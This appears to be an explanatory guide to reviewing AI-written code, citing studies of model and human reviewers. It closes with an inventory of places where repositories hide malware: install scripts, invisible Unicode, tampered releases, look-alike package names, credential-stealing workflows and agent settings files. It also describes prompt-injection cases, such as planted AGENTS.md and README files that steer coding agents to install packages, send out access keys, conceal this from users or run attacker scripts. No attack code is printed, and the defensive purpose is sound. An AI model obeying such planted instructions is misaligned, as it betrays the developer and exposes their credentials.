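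The models' stated reasons give some support to the idea that they find fault too readily. In 48.2% of 4,190 explanations for rejecting correct code, the models claimed an error in the logic, often without giving an input that would show it. They added a requirement in another 14.1%, claimed a mistake at a boundary in 13.2% and misread the specification in 11.7%. Complaints about style or speed were rare. In the shop example, a model might reject `total > 50` because it thinks an order of exactly 50 should ship free, although V3 requires "greater than 50". Asking the model to cite the rule and give an input for which the code breaks it would make this mistake easy to spot.

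A correct verdict can come with a wrong explanation. When GPT-4o correctly rejected buggy MBPP programs, its explanation identified the right type of bug in only 70.8% of cases. In one program, a loop that counted digits stopped at the wrong number. The model correctly said that the output would be wrong, but blamed missing logic when the only fault was that number. A developer or agent who relied on that diagnosis could rewrite the loop unnecessarily.

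### Ask for the reasons first

Jin and Chen's prompts had the model give its verdict before its explanation, so it couldn't use the explanation to reach the verdict. *RTLReviewBench* (Mahmud, 2026) measured how much this order matters by testing 12 models on 114 pairs of correct and buggy hardware designs written in Verilog, a language for describing circuits.

For three of the models that had rejected a lot of correct code, Mahmud varied two parts of the prompt. Putting the reason before the verdict raised accuracy by 8 percentage points on average. Telling the model to trace the logic step by step but still give the verdict first tripled the length of the answers and lowered accuracy by about a point. Doing both raised accuracy by 11 to 16 points, mostly because the models rejected correct code less often.

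In one example, the specification asked for an XNOR circuit, whose output is the opposite of XOR's. Gemma 4 gave its verdict before giving its reason, and said the design was correct, then explained that it was XOR and therefore wrong. It gave the right verdict when it stated the reason first. Taking a majority vote over five answers from the same model didn't help, because the model gave the same answer all five times on 93 to 94% of the designs.

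The findings on explanations are therefore compatible. Justifying a verdict it has already given may make a model stricter without making it more accurate, but if it works through the code first, it can use what it finds to reach the verdict. Models that already reason at length before answering gained little from the change.

### Run the proposed fix

Jin and Chen's remedy is to test the model's correction. When a model rejects a program and supplies a fix, their filter runs both the original and the fix on the benchmark's tests and on extra tests that GPT-4o writes from the requirement.

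| Original program | Proposed fix | What the filter does |
|---|---|---|
| Passes | Passes, with the same outputs | Accepts the original, since the fix wasn't needed |
| Passes | Fails | Accepts the original, since the fix broke it |
| Fails | Passes | Keeps the rejection |
| Fails | Fails | Falls back on the benchmark's tests and lets the model judge again, up to twice |

If a model proposed changing the shop's `total > 50` to `total >= 50`, a test with a total of exactly 50 would show that the change is wrong.

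Averaged over the five models, the filter cut the share of correct programs that were rejected from 69.0% to 28.9% on MBPP and from 54.8% to 16.3% on HumanEval, another set of short Python tasks. It usually let through a slightly larger number of buggy programs, because some of them passed the available tests.

These gains are larger than a team could expect. The filter had access to the benchmark's own tests, which the reference solutions are supposed to pass. A team with tests that good could run them on the code and would have little need for the model's verdict. The remedy is more useful when tests are incomplete, because the difference between the original and the fix points to an input worth checking. Somebody still has to work out the correct output for that input from the specification. The extra tests can also be wrong, which may be one reason the filtered GPT-4o still rejected 40.0%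 of the correct MBPP programs.

An agent that applies its own fix skips this check. In *Fixed or Deleted?* (2026), agents had to review and fix five pull requests that were already correct. Claude Haiku 4.5 changed the code unnecessarily in 16 of 25 runs, and Sonnet 5.5 did so in all 25. Claude Fable 5.1 did so in 20 runs and removed the new feature in the other five. When the same agents first received a report from the study's checking tool, which found nothing to fix, they left the code alone every time. Five pull requests is a very small sample, but the result suggests that newer models still treat a request for a fix as evidence of a fault.

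Even a reviewer's question can prompt an unnecessary change. *Adversarial Review* (2026) describes a task that asked for one new argument in an astronomy library. An agent working alone solved it in 24 lines. When the agent worked with a model reviewer, the reviewer asked what would happen if a user called a certain function separately, which the task didn't mention. The agent added code for that case, removed an existing setting, and failed the hidden tests.

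### How newer models compare

The models that Jin and Chen tested are now out of date, and some newer ones reject far less correct code. Mahmud's hardware benchmark includes models of several generations:

| Model | Correct designs rejected | Buggy designs accepted |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | 1.8% | 3.5% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 5.3% | 0.9% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 13.2% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.4 | 28.9% | 3.5% |
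| GPT-4.1 | 58.8% | 1.8% |

Most of the 12 models still rejected correct designs far more often than they accepted buggy ones. But the models differ so much that it is no longer very useful to say that language models reject correct code unless you say which model.

On harder cases, the main problem is the opposite. In *How Much Effort Does an AI Code Reviewer Need?*, Shen, Zhang and Wang (2026) had three Claude 5.5 models review 90 changes that agents had written for Django, a widely used Python project. All the changes had passed the original tests in SWE-benchVerified. After applying stronger tests and checking the labels by hand, they counted 55 as wrong and 35 as correct. The models could read the whole project and run their own tests.

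| Model | Effort setting | Wrong changes accepted | Correct changes rejected | Average cost per review |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 5.5 | Low | 67% | 6% | $0.04 |
| Opus 5.5 | Medium | 47% | 6% | $0.09 |
| Opus 5.5 | High | 45% | 6% | $0.12 |
| Sonnet 5.5 | High | 49% | 9% | $0.05 |
| Haiku 5.5 | High | 51% | 11% | $0.01 |

Even the best setting accepted nearly half of the wrong changes. If one in six incoming changes were wrong, 90.9% of the changes that Opus 5.5 accepted at medium effort would be correct, compared with 83.3% of all incoming changes. That is useful for nine cents, but not enough to replace other checks.

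Haiku 5.5 accepted few of the buggy hardware designs in Mahmud's benchmark but about half of the wrong Django changes. The Django changes were harder to judge because each had already passed a set of tests, whereas every buggy hardware design failed its ordinary test. The low false alarm rate in the Django study may also be partly due to the instructions in its prompt to reject a change only for an unmet requirement or a significant functional fault, and to report style issues separately.

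The labels in the Django study are also open to dispute. A model reread the original requests and judged that 32 of the 55 changes marked wrong had failed a test of something the request might not require. It found only six where the request clearly did require it. Some of the marked changes that the reviewers accepted may therefore have been acceptable. Two of the three researchers work for Trust My Bot, which makes a tool that puts every change through a model reviewer, although their results are unfavorable to such tools.

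The models may also have remembered the official fixes. Given only the text of each request, Opus 5.5 reproduced 67% of the lines changed in the official fix, not counting lines that appeared in the request. Shen and colleagues had other model instances look for reviews in which this memory decided the verdict. In the reviews they found, the models had accepted 71% of wrong changes, compared with 46% in the rest. Harder changes could explain both the reliance on memory and the higher error rate. On a private project, the models would have no official fix to remember, so their error rates may be different.

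A reviewer's error rates also depend on which agent wrote the code. In *Frozen Judges, Moving Agents*, Li (2026) had three fixed models judge code from many public coding agents on 250 SWE-bench tasks. The judges accepted a larger share of the failed changes from more capable agents. A follow-up with eight configurations of another agent found the same pattern, with an average rank correlation of 0.94. This is probably because better agents make mistakes that are harder to see.

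Measuring the reviewer's error rates once and correcting for them doesn't solve this. When Li used error rates from an older version of an agent to correct its successor's scores, the error in comparing the two rose from 3.8 to 19.5 percentage points. A team that changes its coding agent should test its reviewer again, on recent diffs from the new agent that a person has checked. The sample has to include correct diffs as well as faulty ones so the team can see how much correct code the reviewer rejects.

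## Read the code yourself: why a quick read misses subtle errors

Model reviewers accept many wrong changes, so a team still needs people to read the code. People also miss subtle mistakes, especially when they read quickly. A quick reader sees the names, comments and layout, which show what the author meant the code to do, but may not work out what it actually does.

### One function, read twice

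Suppose an agent writes the function below to apply the shop's vouchers. The text in triple quotation marks is a docstring, a description that Python programmers put at the top of a function.

```python
def apply_voucher(total, voucher, today):
    """Return the order total after applying a voucher.

    A valid voucher takes its face value off the total, which
    never falls below 0. An expired or used voucher changes nothing.
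    """
    # Ignore vouchers that are no longer valid
    if voucher.expires < today:
        return total

    # Never let the total fall below 0
    if voucher.value > total:
        return total

    return total - voucher.value
```

This function looks fine on a quick read. Its name fits its job, and its docstring agrees with the shop's rules. It has a block for invalid vouchers, another for totals that would fall below 0, and a last line that subtracts the voucher. The obvious test, a voucher for 10 on an order of 30, correctly gives 20.

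Tracing the function means choosing an input and following it through the code line by line. The table shows this for a voucher worth 10.

| Order total | State of the voucher | Result required by the docstring | Result from the code |
|---|---|---|---|
| 30 | Valid | 20 | 20 |
| 11 | Valid | 1 | 1 |
| 10 | Valid | 0 | 0 |
| 9 | Valid | 0 | 9 |
| 30 | Expired yesterday | 30 | 30 |
| 30 | Expires today | Unclear | 20 |
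| 30 | Already used | 30 | 20 |

The code has two mistakes. In one, the function ignores a voucher worth more than the order instead of reducing the total to 0. With a voucher worth 10, a customer with an order of 10 pays nothing before delivery charges, but a customer with an order of 9 pays 9. The comment above that check correctly says that the total never falls below 0, which makes the mistake harder to see.

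The other mistake is that the function never checks whether the customer has already used the voucher, so the same voucher works on every order until it expires. The phrase "no longer valid" in the comment could describe both expired and used vouchers, but the line under the comment only checks the date.

The row for a voucher that expires today shows a gap in the specification.

### Why these mistakes are easy to miss

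Someone who has just read the docstring tends to look for lines that confirm it. The check for low totals is in the right place and has the right comment, so a reader can easily assume it also returns the right number.

An omission is harder to notice because there is no faulty line to look at. *From Preventive to Reactive* (2026) describes a coding session in which an AI assistant wrote code for updating a user's profile. The code took the user's identity from the request instead of the login session, so anyone could change another person's profile by altering the request. The participant saw at once that a check was missing. Another participant asked the assistant about further security concerns and learned of a weakness they hadn't considered. The other 12 participants either didn't review for security or were satisfied with code that still had vulnerabilities. The group was small, but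 all 12 had working code and nothing on the screen to suggest a problem.

Tidy code is also weaker evidence of care than it used to be. Clear names, consistent layout and a full docstring were a weak sign that a human author had taken care over the rest, but a language model produces them whether or not the logic is right. *Human-Written vs. AI-Generated Code* (Cotroneo, Improta and Liguori, 2025) compared code by human developers with code from three language models. The models' code was generally simpler and more repetitive, but it contained more high-risk security vulnerabilities. Those models are now old, so the comparison may not hold for current ones, but it shows that simple code can be unsafe.

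*More Code, Less Reuse* (2026) reports that agents' pull requests scored nearly twice as high as people's on a measure of redundant code, yet reviewers' comments on them expressed less anger and disgust. The paper suggests that reviewers may be less vigilant when code looks correct and passes its tests. That is plausible, but the study measured the tone of reviewers' comments rather than how carefully they read the code, and they may have expressed less anger simply because a machine wrote it.

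### What changes when reviewers think a model wrote the code

Reviewers might read code more carefully if they know that a model wrote it. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto et al., 2026) tested this with an eye tracker and 32 software practitioners from 20 organisations. Each participant reviewed four Python files of about 77 lines. People wrote all of the code, but the researchers labelled some passages as the work of a fictional AI tool. Some participants saw a given passage with the label and others saw the same passage without it, so differences in the code can't explain the results.

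The eye tracker recorded how long participants' eyes rested on each passage and how far they jumped between rests. Longer jumps suggest that a participant was skipping text instead of reading line by line.

Participants looked at labelled code for longer, mainly when it was complex. On one six-line passage, the label added about 5 seconds to an average of 15, or 33%. On a 25-line passage, it added about 15 seconds, or 60%. It made little difference on very short passages. The length of the jumps hardly changed anywhere, so Khojah and colleagues conclude that participants spent more time on labelled code but did not review it more thoroughly, though many believed they had.

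Jump length is an indirect measure of thoroughness. A reviewer who stops to work out what happens at a total of 9 would look at the same line for longer without making shorter jumps. The extra seconds could therefore reflect careful tracing or hesitation.

The experiment can't distinguish these possibilities because the researchers didn't measure how many of the planted faults in the files participants found. They also told participants that their performance would not be assessed. An earlier eye-tracking study they cite found a correlation between time spent looking at buggy code and the number of bugs found. But people may look longer at a line because they have already noticed something wrong with it.

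The label also showed the prompt that had supposedly produced the code, and 14 participants used it. Seven used it only as documentation, to understand what the code did. Five treated it as a requirement and looked back and forth between it and the code to see whether they matched, and two did both. Treating the prompt as a requirement is more useful for finding drift, because it gives the reader something to compare the code with.

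A mismatch between a function's docstring and its code doesn't show which one is wrong. In the experiment, `celsius_to_kelvin` had a docstring about converting Celsius to Fahrenheit. The code correctly converted to kelvin, so the docstring was wrong.

### How many mistakes readers find

It is hard to find an adequate controlled study from 2025 or 2026 that counts the faults people find in complete model-written programs, with and without AI help. In the closest study, *Programmers Are Poor and Overconfident Judges of LLM-Generated Assertions*, Kaufman, Murali and colleagues (2026) tested a narrower task. They asked 86 Python programmers, about two-thirds of them professional developers, to judge assertions written by GPT-3.5 and GPT-4. Each participant saw a short function, which they were to assume was correct, and decided whether an assertion correctly described its result.

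The programmers recognised 73.9% of the correct assertions as correct but only 49.0% of the wrong ones as wrong. If wrong assertions are the faults to catch, their recall was 49% and their false positive rate was about 26%, which gives a Youden's index of 0.23. They reported confidence of about 4 out of 5 whether they were right or wrong, and more experienced programmers did no better.

The hardest case involved a function that returns the values two lists have in common, sorted and without repeats. The wrong assertion went through the first list and kept each value that was also in the second list and appeared exactly once in the result. This leaves repeats in, although it looks as if it removes them. If the lists are 1, 1, 2 and 1, 4, the function correctly returns a single 1, while the assertion requires 1, 1. Only 10% of the programmers who saw this assertion identified it as wrong, although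 92% recognised the correct assertion for the same function. Tracing a list with a repeated value would have exposed the error.

Kaufman and colleagues expected comments explaining the assertions to help, but found no overall benefit. Comments that described only part of an assertion led to more mistakes than complete ones. Partial comments also made programmers more confident than no comment at all (average confidence was 4.25, compared with 3.99). A reader of the shop's voucher function faces a similar risk, since "Never let the total fall below 0" is accurate but leaves out what the total should be.

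Programmers who caught a wrong assertion took 123 seconds on average, while those who accepted one took 97. The difference doesn't prove that reading more slowly would have helped, because someone who suspects a mistake will spend time confirming it.

A follow-up study in which ten developers thought aloud gives some support to that explanation. When the developers judged an assertion wrong, they usually worked through an example that broke it, but mostly to confirm a suspicion they already had. When an assertion seemed right, they only occasionally looked for such an example. They relied at least partly on intuition in 12 of their 50 judgments, and seven of those were wrong.

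Readers did better when they could compare the requirements one at a time. One function in the main experiment required all its inputs to be whole numbers. The wrong assertion left out that condition, and 75% of the programmers noticed the error. So people can find omissions, at least when they have a short list of conditions to compare with the code.

The 49% figure comes from participants checking short assertions that old models wrote about correct code. It is not an estimate for ordinary code review, where the reviewer checks the code itself. A whole diff has more places for a mistake, but a reviewer can also run it.

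In the most relevant experiment on the effect of AI help, *Deep Learning-based Code Reviews* (Tufano, Martin-Lopez and colleagues, 2024), 29 developers reviewed small programs containing 48 planted issues. Reviewers found a median of 50% of the issues, whether they worked alone or started from a review by GPT-4. GPT-4's reviews had already identified 42% of the issues on average, so the reviewers who started from them added little. They also concentrated on the lines that GPT-4 had mentioned. Together, the reviews that started from GPT-4's comments covered 371 different lines, compared with 484 for the reviews by developers working alone.

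The programs in that experiment were not written by a model, and most of the planted issues concerned structure or documentation rather than wrong results. A newer model would probably find more of them, but a longer list of correct findings could still draw reviewers' attention away from the rest of the code. Tufano and colleagues suggest showing reviewers the automated review only after they submit their own comments, which avoids this problem without extra work.

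In *When AI Is Wrong on Purpose*, Pădurean, Mahapatra and colleagues (2026) planted small bugs in C code that a model had written for 917 students. In one sorting program, for example, a loop started at the wrong position. The students could often repair such bugs by editing the code directly. But they could see which test had failed, so they knew there was a bug to find, unlike a reviewer whose tests all pass.

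### What developers report, and what happens after merging

Developers are aware of the problem. In Stack Overflow's 2025 survey, 66% of respondents said they were frustrated by AI answers that were "almost right". In a 2026 survey by Sonar, 96% did not fully trust AI-written code, but only 48% said they always checked it. Sonar benefits from such results because it sells code-checking tools. Both surveys rely on developers' own reports and do not measure how well they check code.

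GitHub activity partly shows how people review code written by AI agents. Agarwal, Miller and colleagues (2026) found in *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* that more than half of the agents' merged pull requests in their sample had no human review in mid-2025. By early 2026 that share had fallen towards the rate for people's pull requests, about 14%. But in 40.1% of the agents' pull requests, the only person who examined the change was the developer who had asked for it, compared with 21.5% for people's. It is debatable whether that counts as independent review, and the researchers warn that the answer can reverse the comparison between agents and people.

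Although reviewers miss a lot, two studies of merged pull requests provide some evidence that agents' merged code does not contain more bugs than people's. *How Do AI Coding Agents Contribute to Software Development?* (2026) traced bugs back to the changes that introduced them and found such changes slightly less often in agents' pull requests than in people's.

*AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (2026) studied pull requests at one company. In the seven days after a pull request was merged, its author was 5.3 percentage points more likely to open a bug fix if the pull request was labelled as AI-written. But the author was also 4.8 points more likely to open a pull request for a new feature, so most of the difference seems to come from busier authors. The paper calls the result only suggestive, because the data didn't show whether a fix concerned the earlier code.

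Reviewers also miss mistakes in human-written code, so these results are compatible with the low detection rates. Both studies also depend on somebody noticing a bug after the merge, and a customer who reuses a voucher is unlikely to report the bug.

### A reading procedure

The procedure below is meant to catch mistakes like those in the voucher function. Nobody seems to have tested it as a whole, and it takes much longer than skimming, so it is best suited to small diffs and to code that handles money, permissions or deletion. A tool that ranks the parts of a diff can suggest where to start. The procedure assumes that the reader can see all the text, but some of the text in code from strangers may not be visible.

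1. Predict the outputs first. As when writing tests, work out a few results from the specification before opening the diff, and write them down. For the voucher, the inputs might be orders of 30 and 9 with a valid voucher for 10, and an order of 30 with a used one. Someone who reads the code first may accept its answer of 9 as reasonable. With a 0 already written down, the disagreement is hard to overlook. If the specification doesn't settle a result, as with the voucher that expires today, ask its owner before reading further.

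2. Trace the limits and the error paths. For each comparison, follow a value just below the limit, one exactly on it and one just above it. For each loop, try no items, one item and several, including repeated ones. Then follow every early exit and every block that handles an error, since a demonstration of the feature may never reach them. Write down each variable as it changes, and read the comments afterwards. Do this even when the code looks right, because that is when people tend not to look for a failing example.

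3. Look for what is absent. Go through the rules one by one and point to the line that carries out each. No line in `apply_voucher` carries out the rule about used vouchers. Then consider what the rules may have taken for granted, such as who has permission to make the request, what happens if another service doesn't answer, and whether two requests at the same moment could both use the voucher. Look outside the diff as well. If the shop calculates totals both at the checkout and in the confirmation email, an agent may have changed only one of them, and the diff won't show the other.

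4. Read unrequested changes separately. During the third step, mark every changed line that serves no rule, including deleted lines. Some of these will be necessary support for the requested change, such as an import. For the rest, first ask whether anybody wants the change, and only then whether it works. A reviewer who starts with the second question may approve the banner because it displays correctly. Deleted checks and altered tests need particular attention, since either can make the requested feature appear to work. If the owner does want an unrequested change, have the agent submit it as its own diff with its own rule, so that a reviewer has something to compare it with.

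## List where a repository can hide something

A stranger's repository may contain invisible characters and files that few people open, so even a careful reader can miss what is hidden there. It helps to list these hiding places before running a scanner, because the list shows which parts of the repository the scanner has to cover.

Suppose the shop's developer finds a delivery calculator on GitHub. The calculation might fit in one short file, but the repository probably has dozens of others that install the package, test it, publish it or configure editors. Most of the attackers described below put their code in those other files.

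The developer should make the list from a copy that no editor or coding agent has opened. SafeDep's *Miasma Worm Targets AI Coding Agents via GitHub Repos* describes a worm (a program that spreads by copying itself) that attacked GitHub projects in June 2026. Cloning an infected repository (copying it and its history to a computer) was safe, but opening the folder in a common editor could run the malware. A plain listing of file names and sizes, made on a machine with no stored passwords, avoids this danger. The listing should include names that begin with a dot, which many file browsers hide.

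The list should also cover the packages the project depends on, since each brings its own files. In NYU Tandon's *GlassWorm Malware Hides in Invisible Open-Source Code*, Justin Cappos explains that one poisoned dependency can spread malware far beyond where it started.

### Install and build scripts

npm, the main public registry of JavaScript packages, lets a package run scripts before or after it installs, because some packages need to do things like compile a part written in C++. A delivery calculator written entirely in JavaScript has no obvious need for an install script.

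On 8 October 2026, researchers found a malicious release of the npm package for Tensorlake, a service that runs AI agents in isolation. Mishcon de Reya's *Shai-Hulud Burrows Into The Software Supply Chain* (2026) explains that a script ran during installation, before the developer had used the package, and searched the machine for passwords and access tokens. Tensorlake's isolation offered no protection because the package installs on the developer's own machine. The malware also tried to publish infected versions of the victim's other packages, which is how this family of worms, Shai-Hulud, spreads. Researchers detected the release about 11 minutes after it appeared, enough time for about 13 downloads at the package's usual rate of 12,000 a week.

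Where to look depends on the language. Notebookcheck reports that the TrapDoor campaign published malicious packages in three registries in May 2026. The npm packages ran their code from a post-install script, the Rust packages from a build script, and the Python packages when imported.

A scan of an npm package needs to cover more than the scripts listed in `package.json`, the package's main settings file. Miasma, the worm that SafeDep describes, also spread through 57 npm packages that started their malware from `binding.gyp`. That file normally holds instructions for compiling C or C++ code, so it looks out of place in a package that has none. Other attackers don't rely on installation to start their malware. The Hacker News' *Malicious npm Package indexed-btree Hid Its Loader in Runtime Code Before Removal* (2026) describes a package with millions of recorded downloads that kept its loader,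 the small program that starts the malware, in its ordinary code. Turning off install scripts would not have stopped the loader.

### Encoded text and oversized files

Legitimate repositories contain plenty of unreadable text. Developers often "minify" JavaScript, squeezing a program into a few long lines so it loads faster, and they store images and test data in encoded form. Code that decodes a block of text and immediately runs the result is more worrying, because it hides the real program from readers.

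Miasma did this with a 4.3 MB file, `.github/setup.js`, that was almost entirely a list of about 1.3 million numbers. You could tell the file was suspicious without decoding the numbers, because the `.github` folder usually holds templates and automation settings, and a program that large doesn't belong there. The commit (a saved set of changes) that added the file also had a title about updating dependencies, but it didn't add or update any.

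A file's size can also help hide it. ilsoftware.it's *GitHub, il malware si nasconde dove la ricerca non guarda* reports on a campaign called testmetest, which the security company JFrog traced to 42 repositories belonging to 11 legitimate owners. The malicious files were 12.9 to 13.7 MB each, too large for GitHub's code search to index. JFrog's researchers first found traces in 26 repositories, but the main files looked practically empty in the interface they were using, and they saw the contents only when they requested the stored data another way. A GitHub search that finds nothing is weak evidence that a repository is clean, so it's better to search a complete local copy.

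### Invisible, direction-changing and look-alike characters

Computers store text using Unicode, a standard that gives each character a number. Some characters are invisible, and others control the direction of text, which is necessary when a line mixes English with Arabic or Hebrew. They are normal in translations and emoji, but a line of code that calculates a delivery charge rarely needs them.

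In 2021, Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson at the University of Cambridge described an attack they called Trojan Source. Unicode characters that control text direction can make an editor display code in a different order from the one the computer follows, so a reader may mistake live code for a comment. They also described attacks that use look-alike letters. The Cyrillic а and the Latin a look the same in most fonts, so two different functions can appear to have the same name.

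According to Endor Labs' *How GlassWorm Exploited Unicode Shadows in VS Code Supply Chains*, that work prompted GitHub and other platforms to respond. Attackers have since turned to invisible characters. In October 2025, Koi Security found a campaign, GlassWorm, that used them in malicious editor extensions with more than 35,000 downloads.

Attackers used the same technique again in March 2026. Makari (2026), in *Glassworm Is Back*, explains that they hid a whole program as invisible characters between quotation marks that look empty. A short piece of visible code turns those characters back into a program and runs it. A search for that visible code found at least 151 affected repositories, and others had already disappeared.

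The surrounding changes looked ordinary, with small bug fixes and documentation edits in each project's own style. Makari thinks the attackers may have used AI to write them, because producing so many by hand would be impractical. He says they may also have adapted earlier commits, and his evidence doesn't show which they did.

A simple program can list every invisible or direction-changing character in a repository, with its file and line. Reviewers need this list because they can't reliably find these characters by reading the code on screen. They then have to explain each one. A direction character in the Arabic translation of "Free delivery" is probably fine, but thousands of invisible characters in a string that looks empty are not. Finding look-alike letters requires a separate search for names that mix alphabets.

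### Releases that differ from the public source

People usually read a project's source on GitHub but install the package from a registry, and the two may not match. Some differences are normal, such as tests left out of the release or minified files that don't exist in the source.

The best-known case is the xz backdoor. In March 2024, the engineer Andres Freund investigated oddly slow remote logins and traced them to xz Utils, a set of compression tools that most Linux systems include. The release archives of two versions contained a build script that wasn't in the public repository. The script extracted malicious code from files that were in the repository but looked like test data, so a reader without the script had little reason to suspect them. The person responsible had spent more than two years gaining the trust needed to publish releases.

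A version in the registry with no matching source in the repository can be easy to spot. On 19 May 2026, attackers published three malicious versions of durabletask, a Microsoft Python package with about 417,000 downloads a month. OpenSourceMalware's *Miasma Blight Reaches Microsoft* notes that the versions appeared within 35 minutes and that the GitHub repository had no corresponding tags (labels that mark the source of a release), releases or automated builds, so anyone who looked for the source of version 1.4.1 would have found none.

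The tampered Claude Code extension of October 2026 was harder to recognise. Help Net Security's *Claude Code extension poisoned with persistent SSH backdoor* (2026) reports that the attackers added their code to the start of a minified file and left the rest looking like Anthropic's standard extension. The added code ran before the extension started and let the attackers log in to the developer's machine. The malicious version was on Open VSX, a marketplace that editors such as Cursor use, and no one has reported one in Microsoft's marketplace. Cursor says at most 5,000 of its users were affected. Comparing the whole file with the official build would have exposed the added code, which a sample from the middle of the file would have missed.

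When the source is public, the most thorough check is to build the package from it in isolation and compare the result with the release. If that isn't practical, the developer can at least match the version to a tag and account for every file in the release that isn't in the source. A package that matches its source can still be malicious. SecurityWeek describes a maintainer who unknowingly published malicious npm releases because an attacker had already changed the source on GitHub.

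### Package names

A project normally lists its dependencies by name, and an attacker can publish a package whose name is easy to mistake for a real one. *SANDWORM_MODE* (Raj, 2026) describes a campaign whose packages imitated `claude-code` and `supports-color`, both popular on npm. The malicious packages stole credentials and spread like a worm. A missing hyphen or doubled letter is easy to overlook in a list of fifty dependencies, so it is better to copy each name from the real project's documentation and check for an exact match.

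Some malicious packages don't imitate another package's name, so comparing spellings won't reveal them. Expert Insights' *TrapDoor Crypto Stealer Targets AI Developers in Coordinated Campaign* (2026) reports that TrapDoor's packages posed as generic developer tools and security scanners. The downloads recorded for indexed-btree show that popularity isn't much of a guarantee of safety.

Bad package names can also come from language models, which sometimes recommend packages that don't exist. If a model repeats the same invented name to different people, an attacker can register it and wait for someone to install it. The package will then install without an error, so a successful installation doesn't show that the model was right. Before using a package that a model suggested, the developer should check who publishes it, when it first appeared and whether an independent, established project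 uses it.

### Continuous-integration workflows

Many projects use continuous integration, in which a server builds and tests the code after each change. The server's commands are in workflow files, which GitHub projects keep in `.github/workflows`. The server often holds the passwords and tokens needed to publish a release, so a workflow can be a more valuable target for an attacker than the program it tests.

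On 18 May 2026, a campaign called Megalodon added malicious workflows to 5,561 GitHub repositories in about six hours. StepSecurity, which sells protection for the servers that run such workflows, says the attackers targeted projects that didn't require a review before changes reached the main branch. The workflows contained encoded commands that collected credentials and sent them to an outside server. The step that ran these commands finished without an error, so a maintainer who looked only at the results would have seen nothing unusual.

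The workflow files had ordinary names such as `ci.yml`, and the workflows in them were named "SysDiag" or "Optimize-Build". The commits used invented bot names and routine messages about improving the build. According to SecurityWeek, one version stayed dormant until somebody triggered it, so a record of past runs wouldn't have revealed it.

Downloading a project doesn't run its workflows, so the shop's developer would be exposed directly only after copying the project to the shop's own GitHub account and turning its workflows on. But a malicious workflow is evidence that an attacker could change the repository and may have the maintainer's publishing credentials, which makes recent releases suspect too. Warning signs in a workflow include encoded commands, unfamiliar web addresses and permissions that its job shouldn't require, such as access to a cloud account when it only runs tests.

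### Editor and agent settings that run commands

Editors and coding agents read settings from the project folder, and some of those settings can run commands. Tenable lists legitimate uses for commands that run at the start of an agent session, including setting up a project's environment and checking tool versions. The presence of such a command therefore doesn't prove an attack, and what the command launches matters more.

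One Miasma commit changed or added six files. One was the 4.3 MB program, and the other five existed to start it:

| File | Tool | When the program starts |
|---|---|---|
| `.claude/settings.json` | Claude Code | A session begins in the folder |
| `.gemini/settings.json` | Gemini CLI | A session begins in the folder |
| `.vscode/tasks.json` | VS Code | Somebody opens the folder |
| `.cursor/rules/setup.mdc` | Cursor | The agent follows a written instruction to run it |
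| `package.json` | npm | Somebody runs the project's tests |

SafeDep found 123 repositories containing the same Claude Code and Gemini settings, and considers that a minimum because GitHub's search covers only part of what GitHub stores. The infected projects' commit histories also contained clues. In one case, the worm pushed the same commit to five repositories in 49 seconds, under the name of GitHub's automation account. In Microsoft's durabletask repository, the attacker dated the commit 2020, so sorting by date would have hidden it among older changes.

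It is uncertain how far Miasma spread. Fogel (2026), in *Your agents answer to Hades*, writes that the campaign reached 73 Microsoft repositories. GitHub disabled that many on 5 June, within 105 seconds, but OpenSourceMalware calls the connection between the worm and the wider shutdown circumstantial. SafeDep names two of the 73 as carrying the malicious settings. Microsoft, quoted in TechRadar's *Microsoft disables over 70 GitHub repos after hackers compromised them*, said only that it had temporarily removed some repositories while it investigated.

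Sources also differ on whether the tools ask permission first. Fogel writes that several of these settings run without a prompt, while The Hacker News (2026) reports that such settings files make Claude Code ask whether the user trusts the folder. Both could be right, since tools differ and a user may have already trusted the folder. PromptArmor describes this risk in Codex, where a user downloads and trusts a safe project, and a later update adds a harmful setting. The developer should therefore check the settings files again after every update, before opening the project.

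A setting can do harm without running a command. *Beyond source code* (Quintero and Kapellmann Zafra, 2026) describes two settings files that made Claude Code send its requests to third-party servers instead of Anthropic's, and that turned off error reports and cost warnings. The servers may have belonged to unofficial resellers, but they could still have received the user's prompts, source code and credentials. Any web address in a settings file needs an explanation.

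### Agent instruction files

Files such as AGENTS.md and CLAUDE.md contain guidance for coding agents in ordinary prose, usually about the project's style, its tools and how to run its tests. Prompt Security points out that the AGENTS.md specification has no security model and doesn't distinguish documentation from privileged instructions. An agent may therefore obey text that a person would read as notes.

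This makes instruction files different from malicious scripts, which have to contain commands and be run by somebody or something. An instruction file may contain only reasonable-sounding sentences, leaving the agent to supply the commands. Quintero and Kapellmann Zafra note that older editors needed a person to click "run", whereas an agent can read an instruction and carry it out as preparation for another task, without the developer reviewing it. The developer might have asked only for a summary of how the delivery calculator works.

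Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder* (2026) describes a planted AGENTS.md file that the company Forever Security found on a customer's computer. The file looked like engineering guidelines but told OpenAI's Codex to install a malicious package. Its length (13 KB) and dull tone seem to have helped, because Codex refused a short request to install the package. In Forever's tests, Codex obeyed the file in more than 90% of attempts, and Claude Code obeyed a different file, written by the researchers, about half the time. Forever sells protection against such attacks, and its figures can't be used to compare the two agents because each received a different file.

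The wording of an instruction file can reveal that it is malicious. Quintero and Kapellmann Zafra found one that told an agent to send access keys to an outside address as "maintenance" and not to mention this to the user, supposedly to avoid confusion. No security product had flagged the file in the nearly two months it had been available. An order to conceal something from the user is probably the clearest warning sign, because honest projects have little reason to give one. Orders to skip an approval prompt, turn off a sandbox (a restricted area where the agent can do little damage) or contact an unfamiliar address are also suspicious.

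Instruction files may contain invisible characters, so they need the same character search as code. TrapDoor hid its instructions this way inside CLAUDE.md and a similar file for Cursor. An instruction file may also appear after the first inspection, so the developer should list these files again after installing anything. NVIDIA demonstrated a dependency that writes a new AGENTS.md when it detects Codex. The new file told the agent to add a five-minute delay to programs and not to mention the delay in its summaries.

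Instructions can be in other files too. *Workspace Topology as an Attack Vector in Agentic Coding Assistants* (2026) divides the places into files that an agent loads automatically, documentation such as a README, and source code. The Hacker News describes a README that recommended running a script to check for security problems. When a user asked an agent to test the project's security, the agent read the README and, with no prompt about trusting the folder, ran the script, which started the attacker's program.

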